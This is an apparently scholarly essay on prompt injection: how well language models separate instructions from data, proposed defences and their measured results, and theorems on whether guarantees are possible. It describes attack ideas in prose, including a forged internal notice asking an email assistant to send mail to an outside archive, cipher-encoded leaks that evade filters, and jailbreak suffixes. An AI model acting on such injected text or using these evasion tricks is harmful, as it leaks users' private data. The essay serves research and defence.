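D is any measure of the difference between two probability distributions, and the plus sign means joining strings. If a model joins its two inputs together, both runs receive the same string, so the outputs are identical and the score is zero. This happens in the email client above if its software adds no tags. A model that never executes anything in its data should score high, because the probe changes its task in one run and is just more text in the other.

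Nobody can compute this average over all possible text, so the researchers built a test that needs only the model's outputs. In one item, the task is to classify the sentiment of a passage about a failed product launch, and the probe is the question "What is a group of crows called?" If the word "murder" appears in the answer, the model has almost certainly executed the probe. The practical score is the share of items in which the expected word does not appear when the probe is in the data, counting only items in which it does appear when the probe is in the instruction. A second score, utility, is the share of probes in the instruction that the model executes, as it should.

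The researchers ran 9,160 such items on nine models, putting the instructions in the system prompt and the data in the user's message. They then tried three remedies: a carefully chosen prompt telling the model what to treat as data, a string of tokens found by automatic search, and further training (fine-tuning).

| Remedy | Separation, average of seven open models | Utility, same models | Separation, GPT-4 | Utility, GPT-4 |
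|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 37.5% | 67.8% | 20.8% | 83.3% |
| Chosen prompt | 52.6% | 62.3% | 95.3% | 96.6% |
| Searched-for tokens | 44.7% | 69.9% | not tested | not tested |
| Fine-tuning | 95.5% | 50.0% | not tested | not tested |

These models date from 2023 and 2024, so the figures are not a guide to current products. The first row is also a little unfair, as the researchers acknowledge, because developers train chat models to respond to user messages. Larger models in the same family tended to separate instructions from data less well than smaller ones, perhaps because they could both do the task and answer the probe. Fine-tuning improved separation, but the average model then ignored half of the probes it was supposed to execute. GPT-4 with a chosen prompt was the only combination to score above 95% on both measures, although GPT-4 had also generated much of the test. It still executed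 hundreds of probes that it was explicitly told to treat as data.

A perfect score would not be a guarantee, because it is an average over a fixed collection of harmless questions, whereas SQLCHECK's proof covered every string a user could type. An attacker searches for strings on which the model fails, rather than drawing them at random from a researcher's collection.

### Marking data inside the model

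If the author's identity gets lost because instructions and data share one table of vectors, an obvious fix is to give them different vectors. ASIDE, the method the 2025 paper is named after, does this by rotation. A token in an instruction keeps its usual vector. For a token in data, the software takes the numbers in the usual vector two at a time and turns each pair (a, b) into (−b, a), a rotation by 90 degrees. This adds no weights. The software chooses between the two versions according to where the text came from, so nothing written in an email can change that choice.

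Zverev and colleagues applied this method to six existing models and trained them on about 52,000 ordinary examples of instructions and responses, none of which contained attacks. Separation was 12.3 to 44.1 percentage points higher than in the same models trained the same way with standard vectors and special tokens around the data, and the models lost little usefulness. The average success rate of attacks also fell, from 14.7% to 4.9% on one collection of injections hidden in text and from 45.6% to 28.1% on a set from another benchmark.

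A further experiment confirmed that the rotation was responsible. When the researchers gave the injected tokens the vectors used for instructions and changed nothing else, the model followed the injections almost twice as often.

The label therefore works only as an influence. In the ASIDE version of Llama 3.1 8B, a simple classifier could tell instruction tokens from data tokens with 100% accuracy from the first layer. The model had complete information about where each token came from, and no attacker could forge it, yet injections still succeeded. Pant and colleagues cite ASIDE as an early example of the kind of separation their theorem requires. ASIDE does supply the separate representation, but nothing forces the later layers to act on it, because the weights that connect "this token is data" to "do not do what it says" come from training. SQLCHECK also carried markers with each piece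 of user input, but at the end a program checked the markers and blocked the query.

The researchers behind ASIDE left out safety training to isolate the effect of the design, so it should not be judged as a finished defence. Later work adds such training and strengthens the signal. Kariyappa and Suh (2025), in *Stronger Enforcement of Instruction Hierarchy via Augmented Intermediate Representations*, suspected that a label supplied only at the input fades as it passes through the layers. They gave every layer a learned vector for each privilege level, adding about 400,000 weights to an eight-billion-weight model. Attacks tuned with access to the model's internals succeeded between 1.6 and 9.2 times less often than against earlier labelling methods. *Context-Aware Hierarchical Learning* (2025) adds a further learned vector for each kind of text, to distinguish them more finely.

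A more drastic design reduces how much of the untrusted text the model reads. Zhang, Huang and Gu (2026), in *Origin Is All You Need*, sort tokens into four "rings": the system prompt, the model's own output, the user's text with other permitted content, and untrusted content. They then add a term to the attention score that depends only on the rings of the two tokens:

```
score(i, j) = (query_i · key_j) / √d + B(ring of i, ring of j)
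```

Before the final stage of training, B is set to a large negative number where the model's own output or the user's text attends to untrusted content, and to zero everywhere else. Adding −10 to a token's score, for example, divides its share of attention by about 22,000 relative to the others. On three collections of attacks that were absent from the models' training, success rates were at most 0.05%. Two attacks optimised with full access to the weights succeeded less than 2% of the time. With the attention term switched off in the trained Llama model, between 68% and 90% of attacks succeeded across the test collections, so almost all of the protection came from limiting attention to untrusted content.

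That is also the weakness of the design, because it suppresses honest content in the untrusted ring as firmly as an attack, as Zhang and colleagues acknowledge. An email assistant that applied it to a stranger's email could not summarise the email. The training data avoided this problem because the researchers placed an injected command inside an otherwise permitted document and labelled only the command as untrusted. They labelled the test items drawn from the same source in the same way. A real application can tell that an email came from outside, but not which sentence in it is the attack. If it could, it could simply delete that sentence. The researchers checked usefulness with 805 general instructions, which does not measure how well the model can work with a document that it must also treat as untrusted.

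If engineers fixed B at minus infinity for those pairs, the untrusted text would be guaranteed to have no effect on the output. But this would exclude the text inside the model instead of before it reaches the model. Once the model reads the text to use it, learned weights again determine what the text can do.

### When data should contain instructions

All of these methods need someone to decide what counts as data. Some everyday tasks require a model to follow instructions found in data, but most of the definitions assume that it never should.

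Suppose a user gives an assistant a web page with a recipe and asks it to set the kitchen timers. The recipe says to bake for forty minutes, and the assistant must act on that instruction to do the task, even though a stranger wrote it. If the recipe also says to email the reader's address book to the publisher, the assistant should ignore that sentence. Both instructions have the same author and appear on the same page, so labelling text by its source can't distinguish them, but only the first is relevant to what the user asked for.

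Programmers face a harder version of this with README files, which explain how to install software. A coding agent asked to install a program has to find the commands in the README and run them, and a hostile line can look like one more installation step. The user has asked the agent to run a stranger's commands, so the agent can only tell the good ones from the bad by judging what installation normally requires. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* gives similar examples, such as learning to use an online service from its documentation, and argues that a workable policy would first have to identify the instructions in the data and then decide which to follow. Ordinary security has rules for when a program may run newly loaded code, but nobody has an equivalent for agents.

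Another case is the email from the boss asking for the latest sales file. Ye and colleagues open their paper with a similar example, contrasting a manager's routine request to transfer funds with the same request from a stranger. Better provenance helps here, because a mail system can often verify which domain a message came from. But verifying the sender doesn't establish that the assistant should send the file. A thief might control the boss's account, or the boss might be entitled to the file while someone copied on the email is not. The owner of the inbox might also have asked only for a summary, in which case the assistant should report the request and send nothing, whoever made it.

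Developers can train a model to obey harmless instructions from lower privilege levels. *Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* (2026) describes a five-level model whose training examples include such instructions. This makes the model more useful than one that ignores every instruction in its data. But the model also has to learn which lower-level instructions are harmless, and an attacker can try to write one that only seems harmless.

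Whether a model should obey a piece of text can depend on facts outside the text. Hashemi Natanzi and Tang (2026), in *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities*, observe that the same string can be harmless in an isolated chatbot and dangerous in an agent that can write to a database. Rules for what a model should obey would therefore have to cover the user's purpose, the writer's authority and what the surrounding system can do, as well as the words themselves.

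Even perfect separation of instructions from data would not stop some attacks. Suppose the owner of the inbox asks the assistant to pay this month's invoice from a supplier, and a thief has emailed a copy of the invoice with a different account number. The email contains no instructions, so the assistant can treat it purely as data, follow the owner's request exactly, and still send the money to the thief.

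## Can a guarantee be given inside the model?

Language models learn to treat a stranger's text differently from a developer's, but they still make mistakes that an attacker can exploit. There is a common argument that training can never remove all of these mistakes:

1. The model handles trusted and untrusted text in one shared calculation.
2. Untrusted text has to affect the output, or the model would be useless for reading it.
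3. An attacker can word an attack in an unlimited number of ways.
4. Training covers only a finite number of them.
5. So no defence that relies on the model's learned behaviour can come with a guarantee.

All four premises are roughly true, but each faces an objection that matters for the conclusion.

### The premises one by one

The shared calculation is a design choice. Engineers can label each token with its source, as ASIDE does by rotating vectors and Zhang and colleagues do with rings. *Heads of Security* (2026) also describes a design in which each token belongs to a trusted, untrusted or template channel and learned gates act on the model's attention. But in all these designs, training determines what the label does, so the model has no fixed rule about what untrusted text may do.

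Also, untrusted text must affect the output. Security researchers have a strict property called noninterference. For an email assistant, it would mean that nothing an attacker receives depends on the owner's data, whatever the attacker sends. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, points out that this is too strong for a useful agent. If the owner wants a calendar assistant to answer anyone's meeting requests with her free times, its replies depend on her data, so it violates noninterference.

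Text can affect an output without controlling it. In a parameterised query, the user's search text determines which rows come back, but it cannot add a condition to the query. Dongol proposes a similar standard for agents. It compares the real agent with a reference agent that has the same plan and outside controls, but whose model never obeys untrusted text. The real agent is secure if it leaks only what the reference agent would also leak. Dongol used the proof checker Isabelle/HOL to show that some agents meet this standard, but code outside the model protects them by withdrawing tools before an injection can use them.

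Every model has a maximum context length, so the number of possible attacks is finite. But with a vocabulary of 128,000 tokens, there are more than 10^510 possible emails of 100 tokens, so nobody can test them all. A guarantee can still cover an unlimited number of cases if it comes from reasoning about the mechanism, as the seL4 proof and parameterised queries show.

Training on a finite set of examples does not by itself rule out a guarantee either. Suppose a simple program learns a refund limit of £50 from twenty labelled examples. Its rule may be correct for every amount, and a programmer can confirm this by reading the number. Nobody can read a language model's rule for when to obey text, and there is no written specification to check it against. These two problems do more to prevent a guarantee than the size of the training set.

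The argument shows that training and testing alone cannot provide a guarantee. It leaves open whether analysing the finished model could provide one.

### The inseparability theorem

In June 2026 Pant and colleagues published a theorem meant to close that opening. It concerns a property they call Semantic-Faithful Control. Let s be the developer's instructions, and let u and u′ be two versions of a stranger's text that mean the same thing. The property requires that:

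```
if u and u′ mean the same, then control(s + u) = control(s + u′)
```

Here "control" means the probabilities the model gives to its consequential decisions: whether to refuse, use a tool, write to memory or route a request under a different policy. Pant and colleagues define "mean the same" narrowly, as differing only in encoding. One version might use look-alike characters, end in a meaningless string, or be in base64, which represents any data with 64 plain characters. If a stranger asks an assistant to forward the inbox, the assistant should be equally likely to comply whether the request is in plain English or base64.

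The proof begins by asking how well anyone could tell, from a vector inside the model, whether it came from trusted or untrusted text. If the two sources are equally common, the lowest possible error rate is:

```
P = (1 − TV) / 2
```

TV is the total variation distance between the two distributions of vectors. It is 0 if they are identical and 1 if they do not overlap at all. Suppose, for simplicity, that the vector can only give a low, middle or high reading:

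| Reading | Trusted text | Untrusted text |
|---|---|---|
| Low | 70% | 10% |
| Middle | 20% | 20% |
| High | 10% | 70% |

TV is half the sum of the differences, or (60% + 0% + 60%) / 2 = 60%, so P is 20%. The best strategy is to guess "trusted" for low readings and "untrusted" for high ones, and to toss a coin for those in the middle. This strategy guesses wrong on the 10% of text with a misleading reading and on half of the 20% in the middle. The error reaches zero only if no reading occurs in both columns.

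Developers and strangers use many of the same words, so their text must share some vectors in the table that a model starts from. Pant and colleagues compared published collections of system prompts with 50,000 messages from users and found that 61.5% to 82.3% of the distinct tokens in the prompts also appeared in the messages, depending on the model's vocabulary. They assume that the distributions of vectors deeper in the model also overlap.

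Pant and colleagues next observe that attention carries untrusted text into the calculation behind the model's decisions. They then add the finite-coverage lemma. A message has infinitely many equivalent encodings, or at least a vast number, but training includes only a finite set of them, so some encoding u* is always missing. Correct behaviour on the training set does not determine the model's output for u*, so it cannot certify that output. They conclude that no defence inside the shared calculation can guarantee Semantic-Faithful Control.

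The theorem does not apply to three kinds of system. The first processes trusted and untrusted text in separate encoders that interact only through a restricted interface. The second has hard limits on attention, so untrusted text cannot reach the calculations behind a decision. In the third, a program outside the model decides which tools the model may use.

### Where the proof falls short

The lemma shows that correct behaviour on the training cases does not certify the rest. But in the last step of the proof, Pant and colleagues move from "the defence cannot guarantee that the two outputs are equal" to the claim that the required equality fails, which does not follow. Testing a refund program on four amounts does not certify the other four billion, but the program may still handle every one correctly. The theorem also assumes that only finite training enforces the property, which leaves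 out the possibility of proving something about the weights after training.

A model that always refuses to use tools, write to memory or do anything else consequential is a simple counterexample to the theorem. It makes the same decisions for every input, so it has Semantic-Faithful Control. Such a model would be a poor agent, but none of the theorem's conditions exclude it. Pant and colleagues do assume elsewhere that the model's decisions respond to changes in its internal vectors, but they say that the main result does not need this assumption.

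The evidence for overlap deep inside the model is also weak. Pant and colleagues took 300 sequences from each of their two collections, system prompts and chat messages, and averaged the vectors in each sequence. They then measured the distance between the two groups in Llama 3.1 8B using maximum mean discrepancy, which is zero for identical distributions. It was 0.61 at the start, 0.91 at layer 8 and 0.76 at the last layer they tested. They interpret these values as a sign of substantial overlap throughout, but the measure depends on how far apart the points are as well as on whether the groups overlap. Pant and colleagues set its scale from the median distance between points, and with the usual form of that setting, two tight clusters that do not overlap would score about 0.89. System prompts and chat messages also differ in subject and style, so the test does not show what happens to the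 same sentence when it comes from different sources.

Role tags are a further difficulty. In a well-built application a stranger cannot forge them, although Pant and colleagues call such markers forgeable. The full sequence given to the model therefore marks exactly where the stranger's text begins and ends, though the model may fail to use that information.

Semantic-Faithful Control is also a poor match for resistance to prompt injection. It is too strict in some ways. An assistant that refuses anything in base64 but considers the same request in English violates it, although the refusal may be sensible. An assistant also violates it if adding a meaningless string changes its chance of forwarding the inbox from 0.001% to 0.002%. The property is too weak in another way, because an assistant that obeys every stranger's command, in any encoding, satisfies it.

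Pant and colleagues also ran a small trial in which they gave Llama 3.1 8B and Mistral 7B a system prompt for a financial service, with strict rules about what to refuse. They combined an ordinary question about investments with five kinds of attack, including a fake message from an administrator and a series of escalating requests. Both models refused all five. The attacks did change the length and wording of the replies, but Pant and colleagues acknowledge that this is not a violation in the strict sense, because the decision to refuse stayed the same.

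They have better evidence from earlier research, in which automated searches found nonsense strings that made several models comply with requests they would otherwise refuse. This shows that the property failed in those models. They also cite "abliteration", a technique that suppresses refusals by editing a model's weights, but an attacker who can only send an email cannot do that.

The theorem therefore supports the claim that a developer who wants a guarantee needs something besides good results on training cases, which is a more modest claim than its title makes.

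### Rare behaviours and short prompts

Other researchers have looked for limits with different premises. Wolf, Avnery and colleagues (2023), in *Fundamental Limitations of Alignment in Large Language Models*, treat a model as a mixture of two parts:

```
model = α × (badly behaved part) + (1 − α) × (well-behaved part)
```

Training makes α very small. But when the model reads text typical of the badly behaved part, the weight of that part grows, because the model continues text in the way its context makes likely. Wolf and colleagues proved that a prompt of the following length, in sentences, is enough to bring the model's behaviour within ε of the bad part's, on a scale from −1 to +1:

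```
length = (ln(1/α) + ln(1/ε) + ln 4) / β
```

β measures how strongly each sentence distinguishes the two parts. From experiments with Llama models, Wolf and colleagues estimated that ln(1/α) lies between 18 and 30 and β between 5 and 20. If ln(1/α) is 20, the bad part starts with a weight of about one in 485 million. With β at 5 and ε at 0.1, the formula gives a prompt of about five sentences. If developers made the bad part a thousand times rarer, the attacker would need only one or two more sentences.

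Wolf and colleagues tested this on Llama 2 13B. They could not extract an actual bad part from the model, so they trained a copy of it to behave badly and used sentences the copy wrote as the prompt. The original model behaved worse as the prompt grew, at roughly the rate they had predicted.

The theorem requires the mixture to contain a part that keeps behaving badly after any prompt and stays distinguishable from the rest as the text gets longer. Nearly every text has some tiny probability under a language model, but that alone does not make α greater than zero. If training removed the badly behaved part altogether, the theorem would not apply. Wolf and colleagues also note that a limit on prompt length could, in theory, protect a well-trained model. Their attacker is a user trying to bring out forbidden behaviour, so the result bears more directly on jailbreaking than on injection.

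### The limits of filters

Many products add a second model that reads prompts or outputs and blocks the bad ones. In *LLM Censorship* (2023), Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues applied Rice's theorem to these filters, arguing that a language model can write programs and no checker can correctly judge what every program does. They concede that the theorem does not technically apply to real systems, whose outputs and memory are limited.

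Their other argument does apply to limited outputs. A user can ask the model to encode its answer in a cipher that only the user knows. Any string could then be an encoded forbidden text, so a filter that must block forbidden text in every possible encoding has to block everything or nothing. An injected email could likewise tell an assistant to encode the owner's correspondence before sending it, so that a filter for private data doesn't detect it. A list of approved addresses would still stop the message.

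*No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* (Amer, Kinczel and Long, 2026) shows that, if a model can output any finite string, a filter can block every forbidden output and allow every permitted one exactly when some algorithm can decide which outputs are forbidden. An algorithm can check an output against a list of banned phrases, but no algorithm can decide for every program whether it would ever perform a harmful action. Any filter that blocks every harmful program must therefore also block infinitely many harmless ones.

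However, Amer and colleagues limit the conclusions that can be drawn from this result. If outputs have a maximum length, the forbidden ones form a finite set, so a perfect filter exists in principle, even if nobody knows how to build it. Infinitely many errors can also be rare in practice. For any given pattern of use, some filter blocks everything forbidden and wrongly blocks a permitted output less than, for example, one time in a million. But an attacker does not follow the usual pattern of use, so a low average error rate does not bound the damage from attacks.

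A perfect filter may also take too long to run. In *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*, Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025) used time-lock puzzles, which are quick to make but need a long calculation to solve. An attacker hides a harmful instruction in such a puzzle. The main model has time to solve it and follow the instruction, but a much faster filter cannot distinguish the puzzle from an innocent prompt. The proof assumes that secure time-lock puzzles exist, and it applies to a model built specially to solve and obey them. Ball and colleagues admit that this construction is contrived, but reply that attackers have exploited other weaknesses that once looked contrived, such as one that let thieves take more than $60 million in a 2016 attack on Ethereum, a cryptocurrency platform.

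Ball and colleagues conclude that filters without access to a model's internals cannot make it safe. Pant and colleagues, by contrast, recommend enforcement outside the learned calculation. The two views are compatible because Ball and colleagues consider filters that must judge whether text is harmful, and a program that checks an address against a list makes no such judgement.

A defence can rewrite a dangerous prompt instead of blocking it. *The Defense Trilemma* (Bhatt, Munshi and colleagues, 2026) proves that no rewriting step can be continuous (giving similar prompts similar rewrites), leave every safe prompt unchanged and make every prompt safe. For example, suppose that prompts lie on a line from 0 to 1 and only those below 0.5 are safe. The rewriter must leave 0.49, 0.499 and 0.4999 unchanged. Because it is continuous, it must also leave 0.5 unchanged, and 0.5 is not safe. Under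 further assumptions about how steeply the danger rises, a whole region of prompts stays unsafe after rewriting.

Bhatt and colleagues checked their proofs by computer, so any doubt concerns the premises. Prompts are strings of separate tokens, and a program can let one string through and replace a nearly identical one with a blank. Bhatt and colleagues acknowledge this, and their theorem does not cover such abrupt defences, better training or changes to the model's design.

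### When a forgery looks like the real thing

The most useful recent result, from *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026), does not depend on how a language model works. The paper considers an email that asks for a travel refund and states that the head of department has approved it. The statement may be true, in which case the agent should act, or an attacker may have invented it. If the agent can't check the claim, it has the same information in both cases, so it must act with the same probability p. It then carries out the attack with probability p and blocks the genuine request with probability 1 − p. For example, an agent that falls for 5% of such forgeries will refuse 95% of the genuine requests that look the same.

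This would also be true of a conventional program or a human clerk with the same information. Neither better training nor perfectly separating instructions from data would help.

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian note that their proof does not show that such pairs always exist. An agent could tell the two cases apart by checking for a digital signature from the head of department, or by asking the user. They argue that each way of checking covers only some claims, and that agents working with less supervision will meet more claims they cannot check. This prediction about how people will use agents seems reasonable, but an organisation can also decide that its agent will never act on an approval it cannot verify.

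### Proofs that cover small changes

Researchers have proved security properties of systems that contain learned models, which is the clearest evidence that finite training does not rule out every guarantee. *Certifying LLM Safety against Adversarial Prompting* (Kumar, Agarwal and colleagues, 2023) describes erase-and-check, a defence against attacks that add tokens to a harmful request so that a safety filter no longer recognises it as harmful.

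In the simplest version, the attacker can add up to 20 tokens at the end. The software runs the filter on the whole prompt, then on the prompt without its last token, then without its last two, and so on up to 20. If the filter flags any of these versions, the software treats the prompt as harmful. One of the versions is the original request, so if the filter flags the original, the software will treat the prompt as harmful whatever tokens were added. This holds for every suffix of up to 20 tokens, including ones that no one has thought of.

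With Llama 2 as the filter, the method certifiably caught 92% of a standard set of harmful requests and passed 97% of safe prompts. The 92% is the filter's accuracy on the original requests. Ordinary code supplies the guarantee by trying every deletion, and the learned filter determines how many requests the guarantee covers.

The cost rises steeply if the attacker has more freedom. For a prompt of 100 tokens, the number of versions to check is roughly:

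| Where the attacker can add up to 20 tokens | Versions to check |
|---|---|
| At the end | 21 |
| In one block anywhere | 2,000 |
| In two blocks of up to 20 each | 4 million |
| Scattered anywhere | more than 500 billion billion |

Even the version that needs the most computation does not cover most prompt injections. The certificate applies only to a request that the filter would flag on its own, with some extra tokens added. An attacker who writes an email from scratch can avoid including any such request, for example by describing a routine transfer of records to a compliance system. Deleting words from that email may not reveal anything the filter would flag.

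Randomised smoothing takes a different approach: the software makes many randomly altered copies of a prompt and goes with the majority result. A system called SmoothLLM alters random characters. Its guarantee, which *Algorithms for Adversarially Robust Deep Learning* (2025) sets out in full, assumes that an attack string stops working once at least k of its characters have changed. If each copy has an 80% chance of reaching k changes, the chance that the attack fails in at least half of ten copies is 99.4%. The assumption is plausible for the nonsense strings that automated searches find, but much less so for a polite request in English, which a model can usually still follow despite a few typing errors. *Towards Realistic Guarantees* (2025) replaces the assumption with a probabilistic one, which allows some attacks to survive the changes.

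Cheng, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *Provable Defense Framework for LLM Jailbreaks via Noise-Augumented Alignment*, hide random tokens instead of altering characters. Their software keeps the system prompt intact, shows the model a random selection of the user's tokens, and takes a majority vote over many selections. A selection that contains none of the attacker's changes gives an honest vote. Any other selection might not, so a secure majority needs more than half of the selections to be clean. (Cheng and colleagues use a weaker condition, so their certificates may promise too much.)

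If an attacker has changed 5 of a prompt's 100 tokens and the model sees 50 at a time, under 3% of selections contain no changed tokens. If the model sees only 10, 58% do, but it must then judge the prompt from a tenth of its tokens. If the attacker has changed 20 tokens, fewer than 10% of the ten-token selections are free of changes. Cheng and colleagues trained their model to cope with missing words and reduced the success rate of one kind of automated attack from 84.2% to 1.2%. That is a good test result, but a proof that covers only a few changed tokens does not apply when an attacker writes the whole message.

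Neural network verification comes closest to a proof about the learned weights. One technique, interval bound propagation, follows a range of inputs through the network instead of a single input. Suppose a tiny network computes 2a − 3b and approves a request if the result is positive. If a is between 0.9 and 1.1 and b is between 0.4 and 0.5, the result must lie between 0.3 and 1.0. This one calculation shows that the network approves every request in that range, which contains infinitely many inputs.

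Researchers have applied related methods to networks of a few hundred units, including some used to avoid collisions between aircraft. In larger networks the ranges quickly become too wide to be useful, because the calculation discards information about how quantities depend on each other. For example, a − a is always zero, but if a is between 0.9 and 1.1, simple interval arithmetic puts the answer between −0.2 and 0.2. Errors like this accumulate from layer to layer.

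A range also has to describe the changes an attacker can make. Kumar and colleagues mention earlier work proving that a text classifier's prediction stays the same when words are replaced with listed synonyms. If ten words in a message each have five permitted choices, such a proof covers 5^10, or nearly ten million, versions of the message, but none that contain a new sentence.

### Unsolved, unprovable and impossible

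"Unsolved", "unprovable" and "impossible to prevent" are different claims about prompt injection, though people often treat them as the same. The problem is unsolved in that nobody has yet built a model with a general guarantee of resistance. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* goes further and conjectures that persistent attackers will always evade defences that rely on a model to separate instructions from data. The paper calls this a conjecture because it is based on a long record of broken defences, which is not a proof.

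To call something "unprovable" is to claim that no one could prove it. *Safety Is Π₁, Provability Is Σ₁* (2026) distinguishes two relevant kinds of statement. "Some input breaks this program" is a Σ₁ statement, which one working attack proves. "No input breaks this program" is a Π₁ statement, which one working attack refutes but no number of failed attacks can prove. Turing's theorem implies that no single method can settle such questions for every program.

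The question is not unprovable in this strict sense, though, for a particular model with fixed weights, temperature zero and a maximum context length, because such a model has a finite number of possible inputs. Given an agreed, exact definition of a successful injection, a program could in principle run the model on every input and check whether any injection succeeds. In practice the program would never finish, and no such definition exists. A shorter proof might exist, but nobody knows how to find one for a large model.

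None of these results proves that prevention is impossible, meaning that no model could ever resist every injection. Some narrower aims are impossible, however, such as having an agent accept every genuine request and refuse every forged one when the two look identical to it. If a thief emails an invoice that reads exactly like the supplier's own, no improvement to the model will let it detect the forgery from the email alone, but an employee can phone the supplier and ask.

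## Why system prompts and detailed rules do not bind

A developer who wants an email assistant to behave safely usually starts by writing rules into its system prompt. When the assistant breaks a rule, the developer rewrites it in stronger terms or adds another. This can look like programming, because the assistant often follows the rules.

### Role markers

OpenAI's gpt-oss models, whose weights anyone can download, read their context in a format called Harmony. Each message consists of a special token, the name of a role, another special token, the text and a token that marks the end (OpenAI, 2025). The roles are system, developer, user, assistant and tool, in descending order of priority. The developer message contains what most people call the system prompt.

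In an early version of its Model Spec, which sets out how its models should behave, OpenAI (2024) specified that the application, not the model, always sets a message's role. But no program enforces the priority attached to that role.

Mu, Lu and colleagues (2025) write in *A Closer Look at System Prompt Robustness* that the precedence of system prompts is "not directly programmed but learned". They found that the published template for DeepSeek R1 puts the system prompt at the front of the conversation with no marker to identify it.

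OpenAI's guide says that describing an output format in a prompt, such as the structure of a shopping list, will "only influence the model's behavior". A developer who needs the format every time has to write a grammar and have the software enforce it as it picks each token. The software can discard any token that would break the grammar, however probable the model makes it. The shopping list will then always have the right format, but it may still contain the wrong items.

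### One rule in two places

Suppose a company wants its assistant never to forward email to outside addresses. It can put that sentence in the system prompt, or it can set a rule on its mail server:

```
for each recipient of an outgoing message:
    if the recipient's domain is not company.example:
        reject the message
```

A stranger then sends an email that looks like a notice from the company's records department, asking for the past month's correspondence to be sent to an archive address outside the company. The user has asked the assistant only for a summary of the morning's mail.

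Putting the rule in the prompt makes the model less likely to send the correspondence, and the notice makes it more likely. The notice can also weaken the rule by describing the archive as part of the company, so that its address does not seem "outside". If the model still outputs a request to send the correspondence, the rule cannot block it, because no program checks the request against the rule.

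If the server enforces the rule, the model may still make the same mistake, but the server rejects the message because the archive's domain is not company.example.

The server's rule is cruder than the sentence in the prompt. It blocks even a contract that the user wants to send to an outside lawyer. It does not stop the assistant from leaking the correspondence through a web form or to an accomplice inside the company, and it works only if all outgoing mail goes through the server. But the company can work out these gaps in advance, whereas nobody can list all the emails that would make the assistant disobey the sentence in the prompt.

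### Training a model to rank its instructions

Wallace, Xiao and colleagues (2024), in *The Instruction Hierarchy*, compared the language models of the time to a computer that runs every program in kernel mode, with unlimited access. They proposed training models to follow the more privileged instruction when two conflict, with the system prompt ranked above the user and the user above tool results. A processor enforces such a ranking by blocking ordinary programs from performing privileged operations, but a trained model has no equivalent mechanism.

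OpenAI has since developed the method further. Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues (2026), in *IH-Challenge*, define the hierarchy exactly. They start from the set of all possible responses and go through the roles in order of priority:

```
B_i = B_(i−1) ∩ C_i    if some response is in both sets
B_i = B_(i−1)          otherwise
```

C_i is the set of responses that satisfy the instructions of role i, and B_i is the set still allowed after that role. If the developer asks for French and the user asks for fewer than fifty words, the model should give a short answer in French. If the user asks for English instead, no response satisfies both, so the model should ignore the request for English. A program could apply this rule if someone gave it the sets, but the sets depend on what people's sentences mean, so the model has to estimate them.

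For training, Guo and colleagues wrote tasks with a simple high-priority rule, such as never revealing a certain PIN, and a short program to check whether the model followed it. A second model writes a lower-priority message meant to make the model in training break the rule, tests it, and revises it based on the result. The model in training earns a reward for following the rule, but it could also earn that reward by refusing everything that mentions a PIN. Some tasks therefore contain harmless requests that look forbidden, and refusing them counts as failure. When the researchers left those tasks out, average robustness rose from 94.1% to 95.7%, but the score on harmless requests fell from 95.0% to 83.1%.

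They applied the full training to GPT-5-Mini, one of OpenAI's smaller models:

| Share of tests passed | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Average of 16 tests of the hierarchy | 84.1% | 94.1% |
| Conflicts between system and user | 84% | 95% |
| Conflicts between system and developer | 86% | 86% |
| OpenAI's fixed collection of prompt injections | 44% | 100% |
| CyberSecEval 2, a public test that includes prompt injection | 88% | 91% |

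The perfect score came from a fixed collection of attacks. OpenAI also paid 127 remote workers to break the rules in the training tasks, with bonuses for success, and let them refine their attacks as they went. The workers succeeded in 36.2% of their assignments against the original model and 11.7% against the trained one. Against the trained model, only 0.4% of individual attempts worked, but the workers averaged 52 attempts per assignment. Most of these tasks were things like guarding a PIN, so the figures do not measure how often an email agent would fail.

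The ranking is also coarse. *Many-Tier Instruction Hierarchy in LLM Agents* (2026) points out that developers fix the role labels during training, so models learn fewer than five levels of privilege, and it is unclear whether they can handle many more. *Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* uses five: the platform's rules, the developer's prompt, settings for each user, the user's message, and data. Even with five levels, an email from the user's boss and an email from a stranger both count as data, the lowest level.

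### What models do when rules conflict

Models can fail to follow the hierarchy even when nobody is attacking them. In *Control Illusion*, Geng, Li and colleagues (2025) combined 100 writing tasks, such as a blog post about a trip to Japan, with six pairs of contradictory instructions, such as to write at least ten sentences and to write fewer than five. They put one instruction in the system prompt and the other in the user's message, then swapped them, which gave 1,200 prompts. A program checked which instruction each response followed.

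Six models from 2024 followed an instruction 75% to 91% of the time when it was the only one they received. When the user's message contradicted the system prompt, they followed the system prompt only 9.6% to 45.8% of the time, depending on the model. Adding "You must always follow this constraint" to the system prompt raised GPT-4o's compliance with it on the simpler prompts from 47.0% to 63.8%, and Claude 3.5 Sonnet's from 20.3% to 32.6%.

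Numbering the two instructions and stating which took priority helped more. The rate for Llama 3.1 70B rose from 14.2% to 75.8% when this guidance was in the system prompt and to 79.7% when it was in the user's message. The model was responding to clear wording, and the system prompt's higher rank added nothing.

These low rates show that developers could not count on the system prompt to override a user's instructions. They exaggerate the danger, though, since a user who asks for a short blog post should arguably get one.

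Newer models do much better, though unevenly. *IH-Benchmark* (McCauley, Kan and Martin, 2026) tested 32 model configurations on 2,323 conflicts between instructions, five times each. On average, the models kept the developer's rule in 84.6% of conflicts with a user, and ignored instructions hidden in a tool's output in 69.6% of cases. Overall scores ranged from 32.9% to 97.8%. Claude Opus 4.6 scored 100.0% on the hidden instructions in every run, but when a user pushed against the developer's restrictions on which tools it could use, it kept to them only 81.6% of the time.

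Overall, the models followed a ban on one particular tool 89.5% of the time and a ban on all tools only 53.2% of the time. Yet a total ban is the easiest rule to enforce in code, because the developer can leave the tools unconnected.

McCauley and colleagues also tested stricter wording. In conflicts with users, models followed a plain rule in 78.3% of cases. Adding clauses that told the model to ignore attempts to override the rule raised the rate to 93.2%. Adding a refusal for the model to recite then lowered it to 85.0%. The extra instruction gave models another way to fail, because a response now had to include the refusal as well as keep the rule. The lower rate therefore does not show that models broke the original rule more often.

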